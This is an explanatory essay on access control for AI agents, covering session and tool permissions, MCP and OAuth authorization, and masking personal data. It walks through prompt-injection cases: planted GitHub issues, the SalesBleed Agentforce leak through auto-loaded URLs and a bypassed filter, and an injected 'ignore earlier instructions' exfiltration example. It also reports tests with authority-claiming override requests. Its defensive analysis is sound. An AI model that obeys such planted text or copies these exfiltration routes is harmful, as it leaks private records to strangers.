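# Session, tool and resource permissions for AI agents, and masking personal data before it reaches the model

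## What are an agent's permissions, and what is masking?

An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop. The model chooses an action, the software carries it out, and the model reads the result, until the task is complete. Businesses use agents to answer customers, query databases, write code and handle email. Because an agent can act on real records, an error or a deception can cost money or expose private data. Two controls outside the model limit that harm. Permissions are rules about what an agent may do and which records it may access. Masking replaces personal data, such as an email address, with something else before the text reaches the model.

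Suppose a shop runs a support agent with 12 tools and a database of 40,000 customers, and asks it to answer one customer's ticket. The tools include ones that read tickets, look up customers, send email and issue refunds. This is a fairly small agent. *PRISM* (Luo, Shen and colleagues, 2026) describes an operations assistant with 47 tools and classes 21 of them as high-risk because they can do something irreversible or carry data out of the system.

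### The agent loop and the tool call

The loop usually repeats three steps, which *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents* (Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt, 2025) describes as thought, action and observation. Given the ticket, the model works out that it needs the customer's record, requests a lookup and reads the result, which informs its next thought. *Agents That Know Too Much* (Lahjouji and Colaco, 2026) points out that personal data passes through the queries the agent writes, the rows it retrieves, the values it hands to tools and the notes it saves to memory before any answer exists, so a filter on the final answer comes too late to protect the data in those places.

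A tool call consists of a name and a set of arguments. In the sample call in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the name is `get_weather`, the only argument is the location "New York", and the result is a few lines of text giving the temperature and cloud cover. For the support agent, a call might name the refund tool and supply an order number and an amount. The model only writes the request, and separate software runs it. A developer can place an enforcement point between those two steps. This is code that allows or refuses each call, and because it is outside the model, text that persuades the model does not alter it.

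Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* presented it as a replacement for building a custom connector for each new data source. The Model Context Protocol overview describes a host application that contains the model and a client, which connects to servers that can each offer tools, data and prompt templates. The client asks a server for its list of tools, the model picks one, the client sends the call, and the result goes back to the model. In July 2026, Model Context Protocol (2026) reported nearly half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits. The version released the same day removed sessions from the protocol, so each request now includes details of who is asking. In discussions of "session-level" permissions for agents, "session" therefore means one run of the agent application,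 not a feature of MCP.

The protocol requires servers to implement access controls, and a server may shorten its tool list to match the caller's credentials. Even then, the tool list is not a set of permissions. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) distinguishes availability, which is what the agent can invoke, from authorization, which is what it may do.

Everything a tool returns is added to the text the model reads, and strangers wrote some of it. Indirect prompt injection exploits this. *Kernel-Layer Runtime Defense for LLM Agents Against Indirect Prompt Injection* (2026) describes an adversary who embeds instructions in a web page, email, document or tool output that the agent fetches during its normal work, without ever interacting with the model. Del Rosario and colleagues give the example of a tool result that tells the agent to ignore its earlier instructions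 and send the user's entire chat history to an outside site. The support agent is exposed because anyone who can open a ticket can write whatever they like in it. The model may ignore such text, but if it complies, the shop has a manipulated agent, meaning that an attacker's text is steering what the agent does next.

### Roles, permissions and sessions

The vocabulary of permissions is older than agents and comes from systems built for human staff. In role-based access control (RBAC), an administrator attaches permissions to roles and then assigns people to roles, so that someone who changes jobs needs a new role and not a long list of individual changes. Sandhu, Coyne and colleagues (1996), in *Role-Based Access Control Models*, contrast a role with the older idea of a user group: a group is only a set of users, while a role ties a set of users to a set of permissions. Ferraiolo, Sandhu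 and colleagues (2001), in *Proposed NIST Standard for Role-Based Access Control*, gave the model its formal definition. Its core has five basic elements (users, roles, operations, objects and permissions) and adds sessions to them. The definitions fit together like this:

- A user is a human being. The definition could stretch to "intelligent autonomous agents", but Ferraiolo and colleagues kept to people for simplicity.
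- A role is a job function in an organisation, with the authority that goes with it.
- A permission is approval to perform an operation on one or more protected objects, for example to read (the operation) the table of tickets (the object).
- A session links one user to those of the user's roles that are active at the moment.

Two relations connect these elements. User assignment, UA ⊆ USERS × ROLES, records who holds which role. Permission assignment, PA ⊆ PERMISSIONS × ROLES, records what each role may do. Both are many-to-many: one person can hold several roles, and several roles can share a permission. The permissions available in a session *s* are then the union of the permissions of its active roles:

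permissions(*s*) = ⋃ permissions(*r*), over every role *r* active in *s*

A human support worker might have two roles. The ticket handler role gives permission to read tickets, read customer records and send email. The refund clerk role gives permission to read customer records and issue refunds. The worker's session has three permissions when only the ticket handler role is active and four when both are, because the union counts the shared permission to read customer records once.

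Once a session is open, the standard's CheckAccess function determines whether it has permission for the requested operation on the requested object. If a user drops a role during the session, the next check uses only the remaining roles. An organisation can also set a rule that names a set of roles and a number *n*, and forbids any session from having *n* or more of those roles active together. Ferraiolo and colleagues wanted permissions to last no longer than the duty that requires them. In their example, a cashier who is also qualified as a supervisor must give up the cashier role, and so close the cash drawer, before approving corrections to it.

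In agent systems, "session-level" permission refers to a looser practice. Luo and colleagues report that mainstream implementations authorize the agent once per session and write every tool from every connected server into the model's standing instructions. This creates a session-level grant, a set of permissions fixed when the session starts that the agent can use for any purpose until the session ends. *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (2026) cites an audit of three agent frameworks in which all three controlled which tools the model could see, but none checked the arguments of a call by default. The sample is small, and a careful developer can add the missing checks. In the terms of the formal model, a framework that checks only the tool's name checks the operation but not the object. It confirms that the support agent may issue refunds without checking which order is being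 refunded or for how much.

Attribute-based access control grants or denies access based on attributes of the requester and the resource, such as a department or a record's owner, rather than a fixed role. For example, a rule could let the support agent open a customer record only when its customer number matches the one on the ticket.

### Least privilege, complete mediation and the confused deputy

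In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder offered eight design principles, two of which run through nearly all later writing on the subject. They reasoned that nobody knew how to build a system without flaws, but that good habits could make the flaws fewer and less serious. They presented the principles as warnings, not absolute rules.

Least privilege means that every program and user should work with only the privileges the job requires. Its main purpose is to limit the damage from an accident or error. If something does go wrong, an investigator also has fewer programs to examine, because fewer held the privilege involved. The support agent's job is a single ticket, so under this principle anyone who wants its lookup tool to open other customers' records must justify that access.

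Complete mediation means that the system checks every access to every object for authority. Saltzer and Schroeder advise scepticism towards proposals to save time by remembering the outcome of an earlier check, because that outcome becomes outdated when someone's authority changes. A session-level grant is a remembered outcome on a large scale, since one decision at the start replaces a check on each later call.

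A third principle from the same list, fail-safe defaults, is that access should be refused unless a rule explicitly permits it. A mistake in a list of permitted actions usually blocks something legitimate, and somebody complains, whereas a mistake in a list of forbidden actions lets something through, possibly unnoticed.

For tool-using agents, *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) translates least privilege and complete mediation into tool permissions, argument constraints, user confirmations and sandboxes (sealed environments where code can run without touching anything else). An argument constraint is a rule on the values in a call, such as a ceiling on the refund amount. Least privilege is hard to apply to agents because it requires knowing what the job needs, whereas the user states a goal and the agent picks the steps, often after seeing intermediate results. Zhou and Zhang give the example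 of an assistant preparing a report, which can process the records locally or send them to a hosted service, disclosing them to another party. The smallest sufficient set of permissions therefore depends on a plan that may not exist yet when the session opens. Complete mediation is also harder, because a single action by the agent can set off effects in other tools, other agents and outside services, each of which needs its own check.

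Even a thorough permission check can approve a harmful action. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes a case at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Its compiler, the program that translates source code into a form the machine can run, was in a directory called SYSX. The company gave the compiler a licence to write to files in that directory so that it could store usage statistics there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. The company's billing records were in SYSX too, in a file called BILL, and one day a user entered that name. The compiler passed it to the operating system, which checked the compiler's licence, found it valid and let the debugging output overwrite the billing records.

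Complete mediation did not prevent this, because the compiler passed the access check. Hardy traced the fault to the compiler's two sources of authority, the user who had started it and its own licence. The compiler had no way to specify which one it was using for a given file. A confused deputy is a program that is tricked into using its legitimate authority on behalf of someone who lacks that authority.

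Least privilege would have saved the billing records if the compiler had been licensed to write only to the statistics file. Hardy notes, however, that the statistics file also needs protection, and a user could have typed its name just as easily. A narrower permission limits the damage, but the compiler can still use that permission to overwrite a file the user has no right to change. Hardy's remedy was the capability, an unforgeable reference that both identifies a file and authorizes its holder to use it. The user would give the compiler a capability for the debugging file, and could only give it capabilities they already held.

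An agent is in a similar position to the compiler. It holds credentials from its operator, acts on a user's request and reads text from third parties, and all of this ends up in one stream of words. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) lists three differences from Hardy's case: the model's decision is probabilistic and depends on its prompt, the chain of authority runs through several people and services, and the hostile request arrives inside a document or message, whereas the compiler received an explicit file name. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to summarise the invoices in an inbox, and one message contains text asking for a payment. The agent passes this request to a second agent that handles finance, but the read-only restriction is not passed on. The payment tool receives a valid credential and executes the request. It can verify the caller but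 cannot detect that a stranger's email prompted the call.

*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) uses the term more narrowly, only for cases where a user obtains through the agent a resource that the agent may access and the user may not. For example, an employee without access to the personnel database asks the agent for everyone's salary, and the agent, which has access for administrative work, supplies it. This requires no planted text, because the person making the request is the one who lacks authority. The support agent faces both versions, since a customer might ask for another customer's details, or an attacker might hide an instruction in a ticket.

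### Identifiers, masking and restoration

Permissions determine which records the agent can fetch, but not how much of a fetched record the model sees. To answer the ticket, the support agent has to open the customer's record, which includes a name, an address and a phone number that the model may not need to write a sensible reply. Data-protection rules have a counterpart to least privilege called data minimisation, which Lahjouji and Colaco define as collecting, keeping and disclosing no more data than a stated purpose requires. Masking applies that idea to the text before it reaches the model.

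What to mask depends on how the data identifies a person. A direct identifier, such as an email address, phone number or passport number, identifies one person by itself. Full names usually count as direct identifiers, although two customers can share one. A quasi-identifier, such as a job, town or age, fits many people and identifies someone only in combination with other details.

Suppose the ticket comes from Maria Lopez, a customer whose refund has not arrived. She gives her email address and phone number and adds that she is 71 and the only vet in a named village. Her name, email address and phone number are direct identifiers. Her age, occupation and village are quasi-identifiers, which together probably describe only one person in the country. Software that looks only for names, email addresses and phone numbers would leave the quasi-identifiers in the text.

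After that software has run, the model reads that [NAME_1] is waiting for a refund and wants a reply at [EMAIL_1]. A mapping table, which the system keeps away from the model, links each of these placeholders to its real value. The model can write a call to the email tool with [EMAIL_1] as the recipient, and code outside the model puts the real address back before the tool runs. This step, called restoration, can also apply to an answer before a person reads it. Some forms of masking keep no mapping table, so the real values can't be restored later.

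Lahjouji and Colaco observe that the more an agent redacts or withholds, the less useful its answers become. Masking barely affects the answer about the missing refund, because the model can explain a delay to [NAME_1] as well as to Maria Lopez. But if she had asked whether the shop had misspelled her email address, the model would see only [EMAIL_1] and could not tell her.

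## What can an agent reach when permission is given once for a whole session?

A session-level grant is usually an access token, a string of characters that a program sends with each request to show that someone has authorized it. OAuth, the standard behind most "allow this app to access your account" screens, lets a program obtain a token without learning the user's password. A token has an expiry time and one or more scopes, which are labels for kinds of access, such as `files:read`. Services generally accept a valid token from whoever presents it, so a stolen one works until it expires or its issuer revokes it.

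### From sign-in to tool call

Suppose the shop puts its customer database behind an MCP server, and a support worker starts the agent in the morning. MCP uses a version of the standard called OAuth 2.1. WorkOS's *What is MCP authorization* (2026) identifies three parties: the MCP server, which holds the protected data, the client, which is the agent or the application that hosts it, and an authorization server, which deals with the user and issues tokens. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), part of the latest version of the specification, sets out this sequence:

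1. The client sends a request without a token. The server refuses it and points the client to the authorization server. The refusal should also list the scopes the request needs, for example `customers:read`.
2. The client identifies itself to the authorization server and opens a sign-in page in the worker's browser. Its request includes the scopes it wants and the server where it will use the token.
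3. The worker signs in and approves. The authorization server sends a temporary code back to the client through the browser.
4. The client exchanges the code for an access token, adding a secret value to prove that it is the program that started the process. The authorization server may also issue a refresh token, which the client can later exchange for a new access token.
5. The client attaches the access token to every request, and the server checks it each time.

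The client adds the token to each call without involving the model. The agent may still be making calls in the afternoon under an approval the worker gave that morning, even if the worker is now busy with something else. If an access token lasts an hour and a ticket takes two minutes, one token covers 30 tickets, and a refresh token can extend the same approval for the rest of the day.

The server checks the token on every request, but this check is weaker than the complete mediation that Saltzer and Schroeder recommended. The server confirms that the token is genuine, has not expired and has the right scope. Unless the server's developer has added another check, it does not test whether the agent needs a particular customer's record for the ticket it is handling.

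### What MCP leaves to the server

Authorization is optional in MCP. A server that runs on the user's own machine takes its credentials from that machine's settings and should not use the sign-in sequence. For remote servers that use it, the specification says that the client must state which server it wants the token for, and that a server must reject any token not meant for it. A server also may not forward the client's token to another service. Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* explains that forwarding can bypass controls such as rate limits, and that the second service's logs may record the wrong caller. If both servers follow the rules, a thief can't use a token for the ticketing server at the payment server.

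These rules limit a token to one server, but they don't limit how much the token can access there. The server's developer decides which scopes exist and what each one covers, so `customers:read` could grant access to one record or all 40,000. The specification allows the required scopes to depend on a call's arguments, so a server can, but doesn't have to, require an extra scope for a large refund. Model Context Protocol lists relying on a token's scopes alone, without authorization logic on the server, as a common mistake.

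MCP no longer has its own sessions, so how long a session-level grant lasts and what it covers depend on the token and on the application that keeps using it. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) explains that a server that needs to remember something between calls, such as a shopping cart, now gives the client an identifier to send back as an ordinary argument. Servers must not treat possession of that identifier as proof of identity.

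When a server's first refusal does not list the scopes a client needs, the client should request every scope the server publishes. This rule tends to make tokens broader. Under the specification, the published list is meant to be the minimum for basic use, but Model Context Protocol lists publishing all possible scopes as a common mistake. If a server makes this mistake and also leaves the scopes out of its refusal, a client that follows the rule will request the broadest token available.

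The other rule concerns what happens when a token turns out to be too narrow. The server refuses the call and lists the missing scopes, and the client goes back for a new token. Model Context Protocol advises the client to request the union of the scopes it asked for before and the ones it has just learned it needs:

*S*ₙ₊₁ = *S*ₙ ∪ *C*ₙ

Here *S*ₙ is the set of scopes the client has requested so far and *C*ₙ is the set in the latest refusal. The next request is the union of the two, so the requested set never shrinks. If the support agent starts with `tickets:read` and `customers:read` and its third ticket requires a refund, it also asks for `refunds:write`, and the worker approves. The agent still has that scope when it opens the fourth ticket, which a different stranger wrote. The union is meant to keep the client from losing permissions it needs for other work, and the authorization server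 may issue fewer scopes than the client requested. But the procedure has no equivalent of the rule for Ferraiolo and colleagues' cashier, who has to give up one role before using another.

### The support agent's reach

With 12 tools and 40,000 customer records, a grant that covers everything gives the support agent

12 × 40,000 = 480,000

combinations of a tool and a record. Maria Lopez's ticket concerns one record. Even if answering it took all 12 tools, the task would need 12 combinations, or one in every 40,000 that the agent has available.

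The figure measures how much the permission checks would allow if the agent made a mistake or followed planted instructions. It is an upper bound, because some tools may not act on customer records. It also counts all combinations of tool and record equally, although issuing a refund can do more damage than looking up an address. It is a poor guide to how much work an attacker would have to do, since one call to a query tool might return thousands of records. The shop can lower the figure by removing tools or by limiting which records they can open.

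### Whose permissions does the agent use?

The number of records in that calculation depends partly on whose authority the agent uses. Developers have three main options.

An agent with its own service account signs in as itself, without a user, which cloud providers support for software that calls other software. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization* warns that if the call doesn't carry the user's identity, the services behind the tools can't apply that user's limits, and every call runs with the agent's permissions. *Why MCP security is different* connects this to the confused deputy problem, in which a server with high privileges acts on requests that don't identify the user who made them, as in the earlier example of the employee who asks for everyone's salary.

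When an agent impersonates the user, the service can't distinguish the agent's credentials from the user's own. This happens, for example, when a developer copies a personal access token into the settings of a local MCP server. The agent can't exceed the user's permissions, but it may have all of them, and the logs record its actions as the user's.

An agent can also act on the user's behalf through token exchange, an OAuth procedure defined in the standard RFC 8693. The agent's software sends the authorization server the user's token, together with one that identifies the agent. It receives a new token that can name both of them, have fewer scopes than the original and work at only one service. The agent's permissions can then be the overlap of three sets:

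usable permissions = permissions(user) ∩ permissions(agent) ∩ scopes(token)

The standard makes this overlap possible, but it takes effect only if the authorization server issues a narrower token and the service checks both identities. Token exchange also fits the MCP rule against forwarding tokens, since a server that needs to call another service can obtain a separate token for that service.

| Arrangement | Permissions that apply | Who appears in the log | Records within reach when a support worker runs the agent |
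|---|---|---|---|
| Own service account | The agent's | The agent | Whatever the account can open, often all 40,000 |
| Impersonating the user | The user's | The user | Whatever the worker can open |
| Token exchange | Those shared by the user, the agent and the token | Both | The same as the worker, or fewer |

Token exchange makes it clear who is responsible, but it may barely reduce the support agent's reach. Support workers can usually open any customer's record, since they don't know who will write in next. If the worker can open 40,000 records, an agent acting for the worker can too, unless the new token is narrower. But if Maria Lopez signs in to the shop's website and the agent acts on her behalf, it can open only her record, because that is all she can open. An agent that answers emailed tickets overnight has no signed-in customer whose limits it could use, so the shop will probably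 give it a service account.

### Why broad grants are common

A single grant is simple to build because there is one sign-in, one token and one place to look when something stops working. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) project argues that general-purpose clients should request all the published scopes at once, because they rarely know enough about a particular service to choose among them, and let the authorization server and the user decide at the consent screen. This also minimizes interruptions.

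Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, points out that agents may keep working across several systems long after the user was last involved, and may find partway through that they need more privileges. If an agent's token expired overnight and only a person could renew it, the job would stop until someone did. Tabata sees refresh tokens and step-by-step requests for more scopes as ways to keep such work usable and secure, and notes that businesses have used similar arrangements for background jobs for years.

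Some companies remove the prompts. rohitraj.tech's *MCP Server Authentication in 2026* (2026) describes an MCP extension from June 2026 that lets a company's login system grant access to every approved server when an employee signs in. An administrator then chooses once for everybody, probably knowing more than the average employee but not knowing what any particular task will need.

The consent screen is the weak point in the defence. A user who approves a list of scopes at the start does so before the agent has planned its work, and Model Context Protocol warns that people turn down requests with too many scopes. It also lists the problems a broad token causes after something goes wrong. A thief can use the token to reach unrelated data, revoking it interrupts all the agent's work at once, and the logs record one broad permission instead of the purpose of each operation.

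Attackers can also exploit consent that a service remembers. An MCP server that connects to an outside service may use one fixed identity there for all its clients. Once a user has approved that identity, a cookie in the browser can cause the outside service to skip the consent screen. An attacker who registers a client and persuades the user to follow a link can then gain access that the user never approved. MCP requires such servers to record consent separately for each client.

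Defenders of session-wide permission are right that more prompts would not necessarily help, because people who see too many stop reading them. But a narrower grant does not always need a prompt. The shop's own software could issue a new token for each ticket without asking anyone, though somebody would have to work out in advance what a ticket requires.

Organisations seem to put that work off. *AI agent permissions are outrunning security* (Zorz, 2026) reports a survey of 1,100 IT and security decision-makers, 70% of whom said they now let AI take actions that would have required human approval a year earlier. Only a quarter chose explicitly defining what an agent may do as one of their two main controls for AI, making it the least chosen option. While 84% said they could see how AI systems reach data and other systems, 49% could see and audit every action. Raghu Nandakumara of Illumio,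 which sells software for containing attacks, told Zorz that "no one wants to disrupt the workflow that made it useful", so the planned tightening rarely happens.

Illumio has a commercial interest in that explanation, and none of the figures Zorz reports measures session-level grants. The figures suggest that broad grants are common but don't show how common. The audit of three agent frameworks described earlier is more direct evidence, but it covers only their default settings.

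### One token for public and private repositories

In May 2025 the security company Invariant Labs showed in *GitHub MCP Exploited* how a stranger could take advantage of a broad grant of permission. In its example, a user keeps public and private repositories on GitHub, a site for storing and sharing code. The user has connected the account to Claude Desktop, an application for Anthropic's models, through GitHub's MCP server. Anyone can post an issue, such as a bug report, on a public repository. The researchers posted one containing instructions for the agent. Then, acting as the user, they asked the agent to look at the repository's open issues.

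The agent, which ran on Claude 4 Opus, read the planted issue and followed its instructions. It took information from the private repositories, including the user's salary and a plan to move to South America, and published it in a pull request (a proposed code change) on the public one. The researchers had prepared the repositories for the demonstration, so the case shows that the attack was possible, but not that anyone had used it against a real victim.

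The user's request concerned one public repository, but the connection also covered the private ones. heise's *Attack via GitHub MCP server* attributes this to the agent's use of the user's account. GitHub's server had no bug in the ordinary sense, and the user was entitled to make every call the agent made. Invariant Labs concluded that GitHub could not solve the problem by changing the server alone.

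Claude Desktop asks the user to confirm each tool call by default, so a careful user could have refused the calls that opened private repositories. Invariant Labs argues that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. This is plausible, but the company gives no figures, and DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* reports it as something the researchers suspect.

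A token limited to the public repository would have kept the agent from fetching anything private. Invariant Labs recommends limiting agents to the repositories they need, but considers ordinary token permissions too rigid for much agent work. It proposes a session history check, a rule that allows or blocks a call based on what the agent has already done, and it sells software that enforces such rules. In this case, once the agent has used one repository, the rule blocks calls to any other for the rest of the session. That would have stopped the demonstration, but it would also stop a developer from having the agent copy a fix from one repository to another.

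That August, GitHub added a different safeguard by scanning tool calls that involve public repositories for secrets such as access credentials, to catch them before they leave the user's control (GitHub, 2025). The scan might catch a stolen password, but it would not catch a salary or a plan to emigrate, because these are not credentials.

### SalesBleed

A more recent case involved business records like those the support agent handles. SalesBleed is the security company Zenity Labs' name for a set of weaknesses in Agentforce, the AI agent platform of Salesforce, whose software companies use to manage customer information. Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature stores what a visitor types into a public web form as a "lead", the record of a potential customer. Zenity reported on 24 September 2026 that text planted in such a form could hijack an agent that later processed the lead (summarised in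 Poireault, 2026, *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk*). The attacker did not need to log in to the company's system.

The planted text stayed in the database as an ordinary record until an employee asked the agent to deal with it. The agent then looked up other records and put what it found into a web address. Programs often load images and link previews automatically, and loading this address sent the data to the attacker without anyone clicking on it. Salesforce's Trusted URLs filter was meant to block unapproved addresses, but the researchers found a way around it. *Один вредоносный лид против всей CRM* (Antipov, 2026) reports that the agent could tell the employee that security rules had blocked the content when the data had already left.

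The employee had asked about one lead. *Salesforce Agentforceの「SalesBleed」脆弱性* (三村, 2026) reports that the agent in Zenity's test environment also had permission to read Accounts, the records of existing business customers. The researchers extracted company names and deal sizes, but Zenity, quoted by Poireault, says the planted text could have requested anything the agent's query tool could reach, which typically includes accounts, contacts and more.

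The accounts of the case differ on whose permissions the agent used. 三村 says the agent used its own legitimate permissions, while Antipov describes access within the employee's rights. In both accounts the agent was allowed to read the records, so checking only that permission would not have stopped the queries.

Another weakness affected Slack, a workplace messaging service. A manipulated agent could post phishing messages in a company's internal channels without asking the employee to confirm them. Colleagues would see a message from a familiar company tool, with no clear sign of who had triggered it.

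Zenity and Salesforce took almost four months to get from the first report to publication:

- **1 June 2026:** Zenity reported the weaknesses to Salesforce.
- **18–19 August:** Salesforce fixed the Trusted URLs filter. Poireault dates the fix to 18 August, and 三村 and Antipov say that it was confirmed on 19 August.
- **20 August:** Zenity confirmed that Slack messages now showed who had triggered them.
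- **21 September:** Zenity confirmed that the whole attack no longer worked. Risky Slack actions now require the user's approval by default.
- **24 September:** Zenity published its findings.

三村 found no sign in the published material that anyone had used the attack in practice. The fixes described deal with how data or messages leave the agent. None reduces the number of records the agent can query, so a company that wants to limit this has to change the agent's permissions.

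Similar attacks keep recurring. Salesforce had begun enforcing its list of trusted addresses after ForcedLeak, a comparable weakness in Agentforce reported by The Hacker News (2025). In April 2026, OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks* (2026) recorded that another company, Capsule Security, had used public forms to extract data through Agentforce and Microsoft's Copilot Studio. Both vendors issued patches. But blocking one way of extracting data leaves the agent with access to the same records, so an attacker who found another way could still extract them.

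### Permissions that end with the task

In guidance from July 2026, Microsoft describes how agents tend to accumulate broad access. A team gives an agent a general "Reader" role because that is quick and the first use only involves reading. Later the team wants the agent to fix the problems it finds, so they add write access, often more than the agent needs, and nobody redesigns the role. Teams also grant administrator roles to get a trial running and leave them in place once it works. Microsoft says teams consistently fail to establish whether an agent is acting under its own identity, a user's delegated authority or a mixture, which makes it hard to find out after an incident who authorized what.

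Its main recommendation is to separate the agent's identity from its privileges. Each agent should have its own identity that stays the same from task to task, with a named human owner and a written purpose. The agent should start with a minimal role, receive extra permissions only for the workflow that needs them, and automatically lose them when that workflow ends. Roles should match small units of work, such as drafting a ticket, with separate roles for reading and writing. Deletions, exports and privilege changes should need additional approval.

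For the support agent, this would mean a basic role that can read tickets. When a ticket calls for a refund, the agent would receive permission to issue one and lose it when the ticket closes, before it reads the next stranger's message. Under MCP's procedure for adding scopes, however, the client keeps requesting `refunds:write` each time it needs a new token. A developer can still make the refund permission temporary by having the authorization server issue short-lived tokens for individual tasks and refuse to carry old scopes forward.

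Microsoft also wants every service behind the agent to check roles and scopes on each call, rather than assume an earlier component has done so. It warns against relying on a prompt to tell the agent what it may do, because planted text can undermine the prompt.

This advice comes from a company that sells identity software, and it includes no measurements of how much harm the measures prevent or how much work they disrupt. In the SalesBleed case, a role limited to leads would have blocked access to the Accounts records, but not to the strangers' contact details in the leads themselves. The shop would have a similar problem if it made the support agent's access temporary but no narrower, because an agent that can open all 40,000 records for two minutes can still copy many of them.

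## What changes when each tool needs its own permission?

Most of the shop's tickets need only three of the support agent's 12 tools: the ones that read tickets, look up customers and send email. A tool-level permission is a rule saying which tools an agent may call, and the shop could use one to withdraw the other nine, including the refund tool. The number of tool and record combinations within reach then falls from 480,000 to

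3 × 40,000 = 120,000

Maria Lopez's ticket needs three of those combinations, so the agent still has 40,000 times as many as the job requires. Restricting tools doesn't reduce the number of records the agent can reach. The count slightly understates the rule's benefit, though, because the nine withdrawn tools include the most dangerous ones. Text planted in a ticket can no longer make the agent issue a refund, but it can still make the agent look up another customer's address and email it to a stranger, because the job needs the lookup and email tools.

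### Checking the list and checking the call

An agent requests a list of its tools and sends calls to use them (`tools/list` and `tools/call` in MCP), so software can enforce a tool-level permission at either point. *Prompts Don't Protect* (Uppala, 2026) describes a proxy, a program between the agent and the tools, that checks both requests. Each tool has a label such as "payments" or "analytics". Each agent presents a signed token stating its role, and a policy file lists the labels each role may use. When the agent requests the list, the proxy returns only the tools that the agent's role may use. When the agent sends a call, the proxy looks the tool up again and refuses the call if the role doesn't cover it.

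Filtering the list keeps forbidden tools out of the model's context, the text it reads before it chooses an action. If a refund tool has never appeared there, the model is unlikely to plan its reply around issuing a refund. Filtering also shortens the list, which matters when a company has hundreds of tools. Uppala estimates that listing the permitted tools in a prompt for a 500-tool registry would take about 25,000 tokens per request (here, tokens are the word fragments that models read, not access tokens).

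But filtering the list doesn't block calls to the tools left off it. A tool call is text that the model writes, and that text can name any tool. The model might guess a likely name, such as `issue_refund` in a shop, or copy one that an attacker has typed into a ticket. If nothing checks the call, the refund goes through. The list can also be out of date. If an administrator withdraws the refund tool at noon, an agent that fetched its list that morning still has the tool on it. Saltzer and Schroeder's distrust of remembered permission checks applies to remembered lists too.

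The check on calls provides the security, and would do so even if the model could see every tool. The filtered list mainly helps the model work sensibly within its limits. Neither takes much time. In Uppala's test on a single machine, the proxy typically took 1.5 milliseconds to produce a list, while a model usually needs at least half a second to respond.

### Telling the model its limits

A simpler approach is to write the limits into the model's instructions and trust the model to follow them. Uppala tested this with a registry of 507 tools, modelled on those of real services such as Stripe and Slack, and 200 tasks in which the most suitable tool was one the agent was not allowed to use. Some tasks named the forbidden operation, some only implied it, some began with a harmless request, and in some the user claimed special authority. In one of these last tasks, a person claiming to be the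 chief financial officer orders an analytics agent to override the access controls and refund $5,000.

Three models attempted every task under three conditions. In the first, they saw both permitted and forbidden tools, with no guidance. In the second, they also saw an allowlist naming the tools they were permitted to use, with an instruction to use no others. In the third, the proxy had already removed the forbidden tools. The table shows how often each model chose a forbidden tool.

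| Model | No guidance | Allowlist in the prompt | Forbidden tools removed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 48.5% | 37.0% | 0% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 66.0% | 4.0% | 0% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 68.5% | 11.5% | 0% |

The figures for no guidance come from models that hadn't been told any tool was off limits, so choosing the refund tool was a reasonable response to a refund request. Uppala's abstract attributes these figures to models that had been explicitly told not to use the tools, which doesn't match the description of the experiment. The allowlist results are a fairer test of whether models follow written limits. The limits helped all three models, and Llama a great deal, but none of the models followed them every time. Haiku still chose a forbidden tool in 22% of the tasks that claimed special authority.

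Even those results probably overstate the problem, because Uppala's settings forced the models to call a tool in every task. A model that recognised a forbidden request couldn't decline it and could at best call a permitted tool that didn't fit. Uppala later let the models decide whether to call a tool, using new requests that included 100 that no permitted tool could satisfy. With the allowlist in the prompt, Haiku made no call in 99% of those 100, compared with 35% for Qwen and 13% for Llama. Uppala doesn't report how many of the remaining calls went to forbidden tools, so the table can't be corrected. If the new requests were comparable to the old ones, most of Haiku's 11.5% came from being forced to call a tool.

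The choice of models is another limitation. Qwen 2.5 7B and Llama 3.1 8B are small models from 2024, and Haiku 4.5 is the small model in an older Anthropic family. A current large model might follow an allowlist more reliably. Uppala notes that Llama did better than Haiku and argues that general ability doesn't predict compliance, but three models are too few to settle that.

The zeros follow from the proxy's design, because any model that has to choose from a list of permitted tools will choose a permitted one. The result confirms that the proxy works as designed but adds nothing to what we know about models. It is still the best argument for the proxy, because an operator can rely on the limit without testing each new model. However, the zeros don't cover misuse of permitted tools, and an agent with the "payments" label can use every tool that carries it. Uppala also assumes that nobody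 has tampered with the registry of tools, and excludes cases where an agent passes work to another agent with broader permissions, as in the earlier example of the emailed payment request.

Filtering the tool list had no consistent effect on how well the models handled legitimate requests. Uppala also tested 140 of these requests in the setting where the models could choose whether to call a tool. Llama got 77.9% exactly right with the allowlist and 82.1% with the filtered list. Qwen dropped from 60.7% to 48.6%, and Haiku stayed below 20% in every condition. The proxy refused none of the permitted calls that the models attempted, so Qwen's drop must come from how it reacted to the shorter list.

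### Granting only the functions a task needs

In all of Uppala's tasks, the pressure came from the person instructing the agent. Alhindi (2026), in *Taming AI Agents with seL4*, instead tested tool-level permissions against indirect prompt injection. seL4 is a microkernel, the small core of an operating system that controls what each program can reach. It has about 10,000 lines of code, and computer-checked mathematical proofs show that certain versions enforce their access rules. It controls access through capabilities, the unforgeable references that Hardy proposed. Alhindi ran an agent in its own compartment and gave it a separate capability for each function it could call, and the kernel blocked every other call.

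The test used AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives an agent tasks such as paying a bill, plants an attacker's instruction in the data its tools return, and scores whether the agent completes the task and whether the attack succeeds. Alhindi ran the banking and Slack parts, which contain 37 tasks without an attack and 249 cases with one, three times each on gpt-4o-mini, a small OpenAI model from 2024. The agent was allowed to call every function in the control condition, but only the functions its task needed in the restricted condition. The model saw the full list of functions in both conditions, so the experiment tests only the check on calls.

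The restriction cut the attack success rate from 48% to 7%. In the restricted runs, the manipulated agent attempted 2,095 calls to functions it didn't have permission to use, and the kernel blocked all of them.

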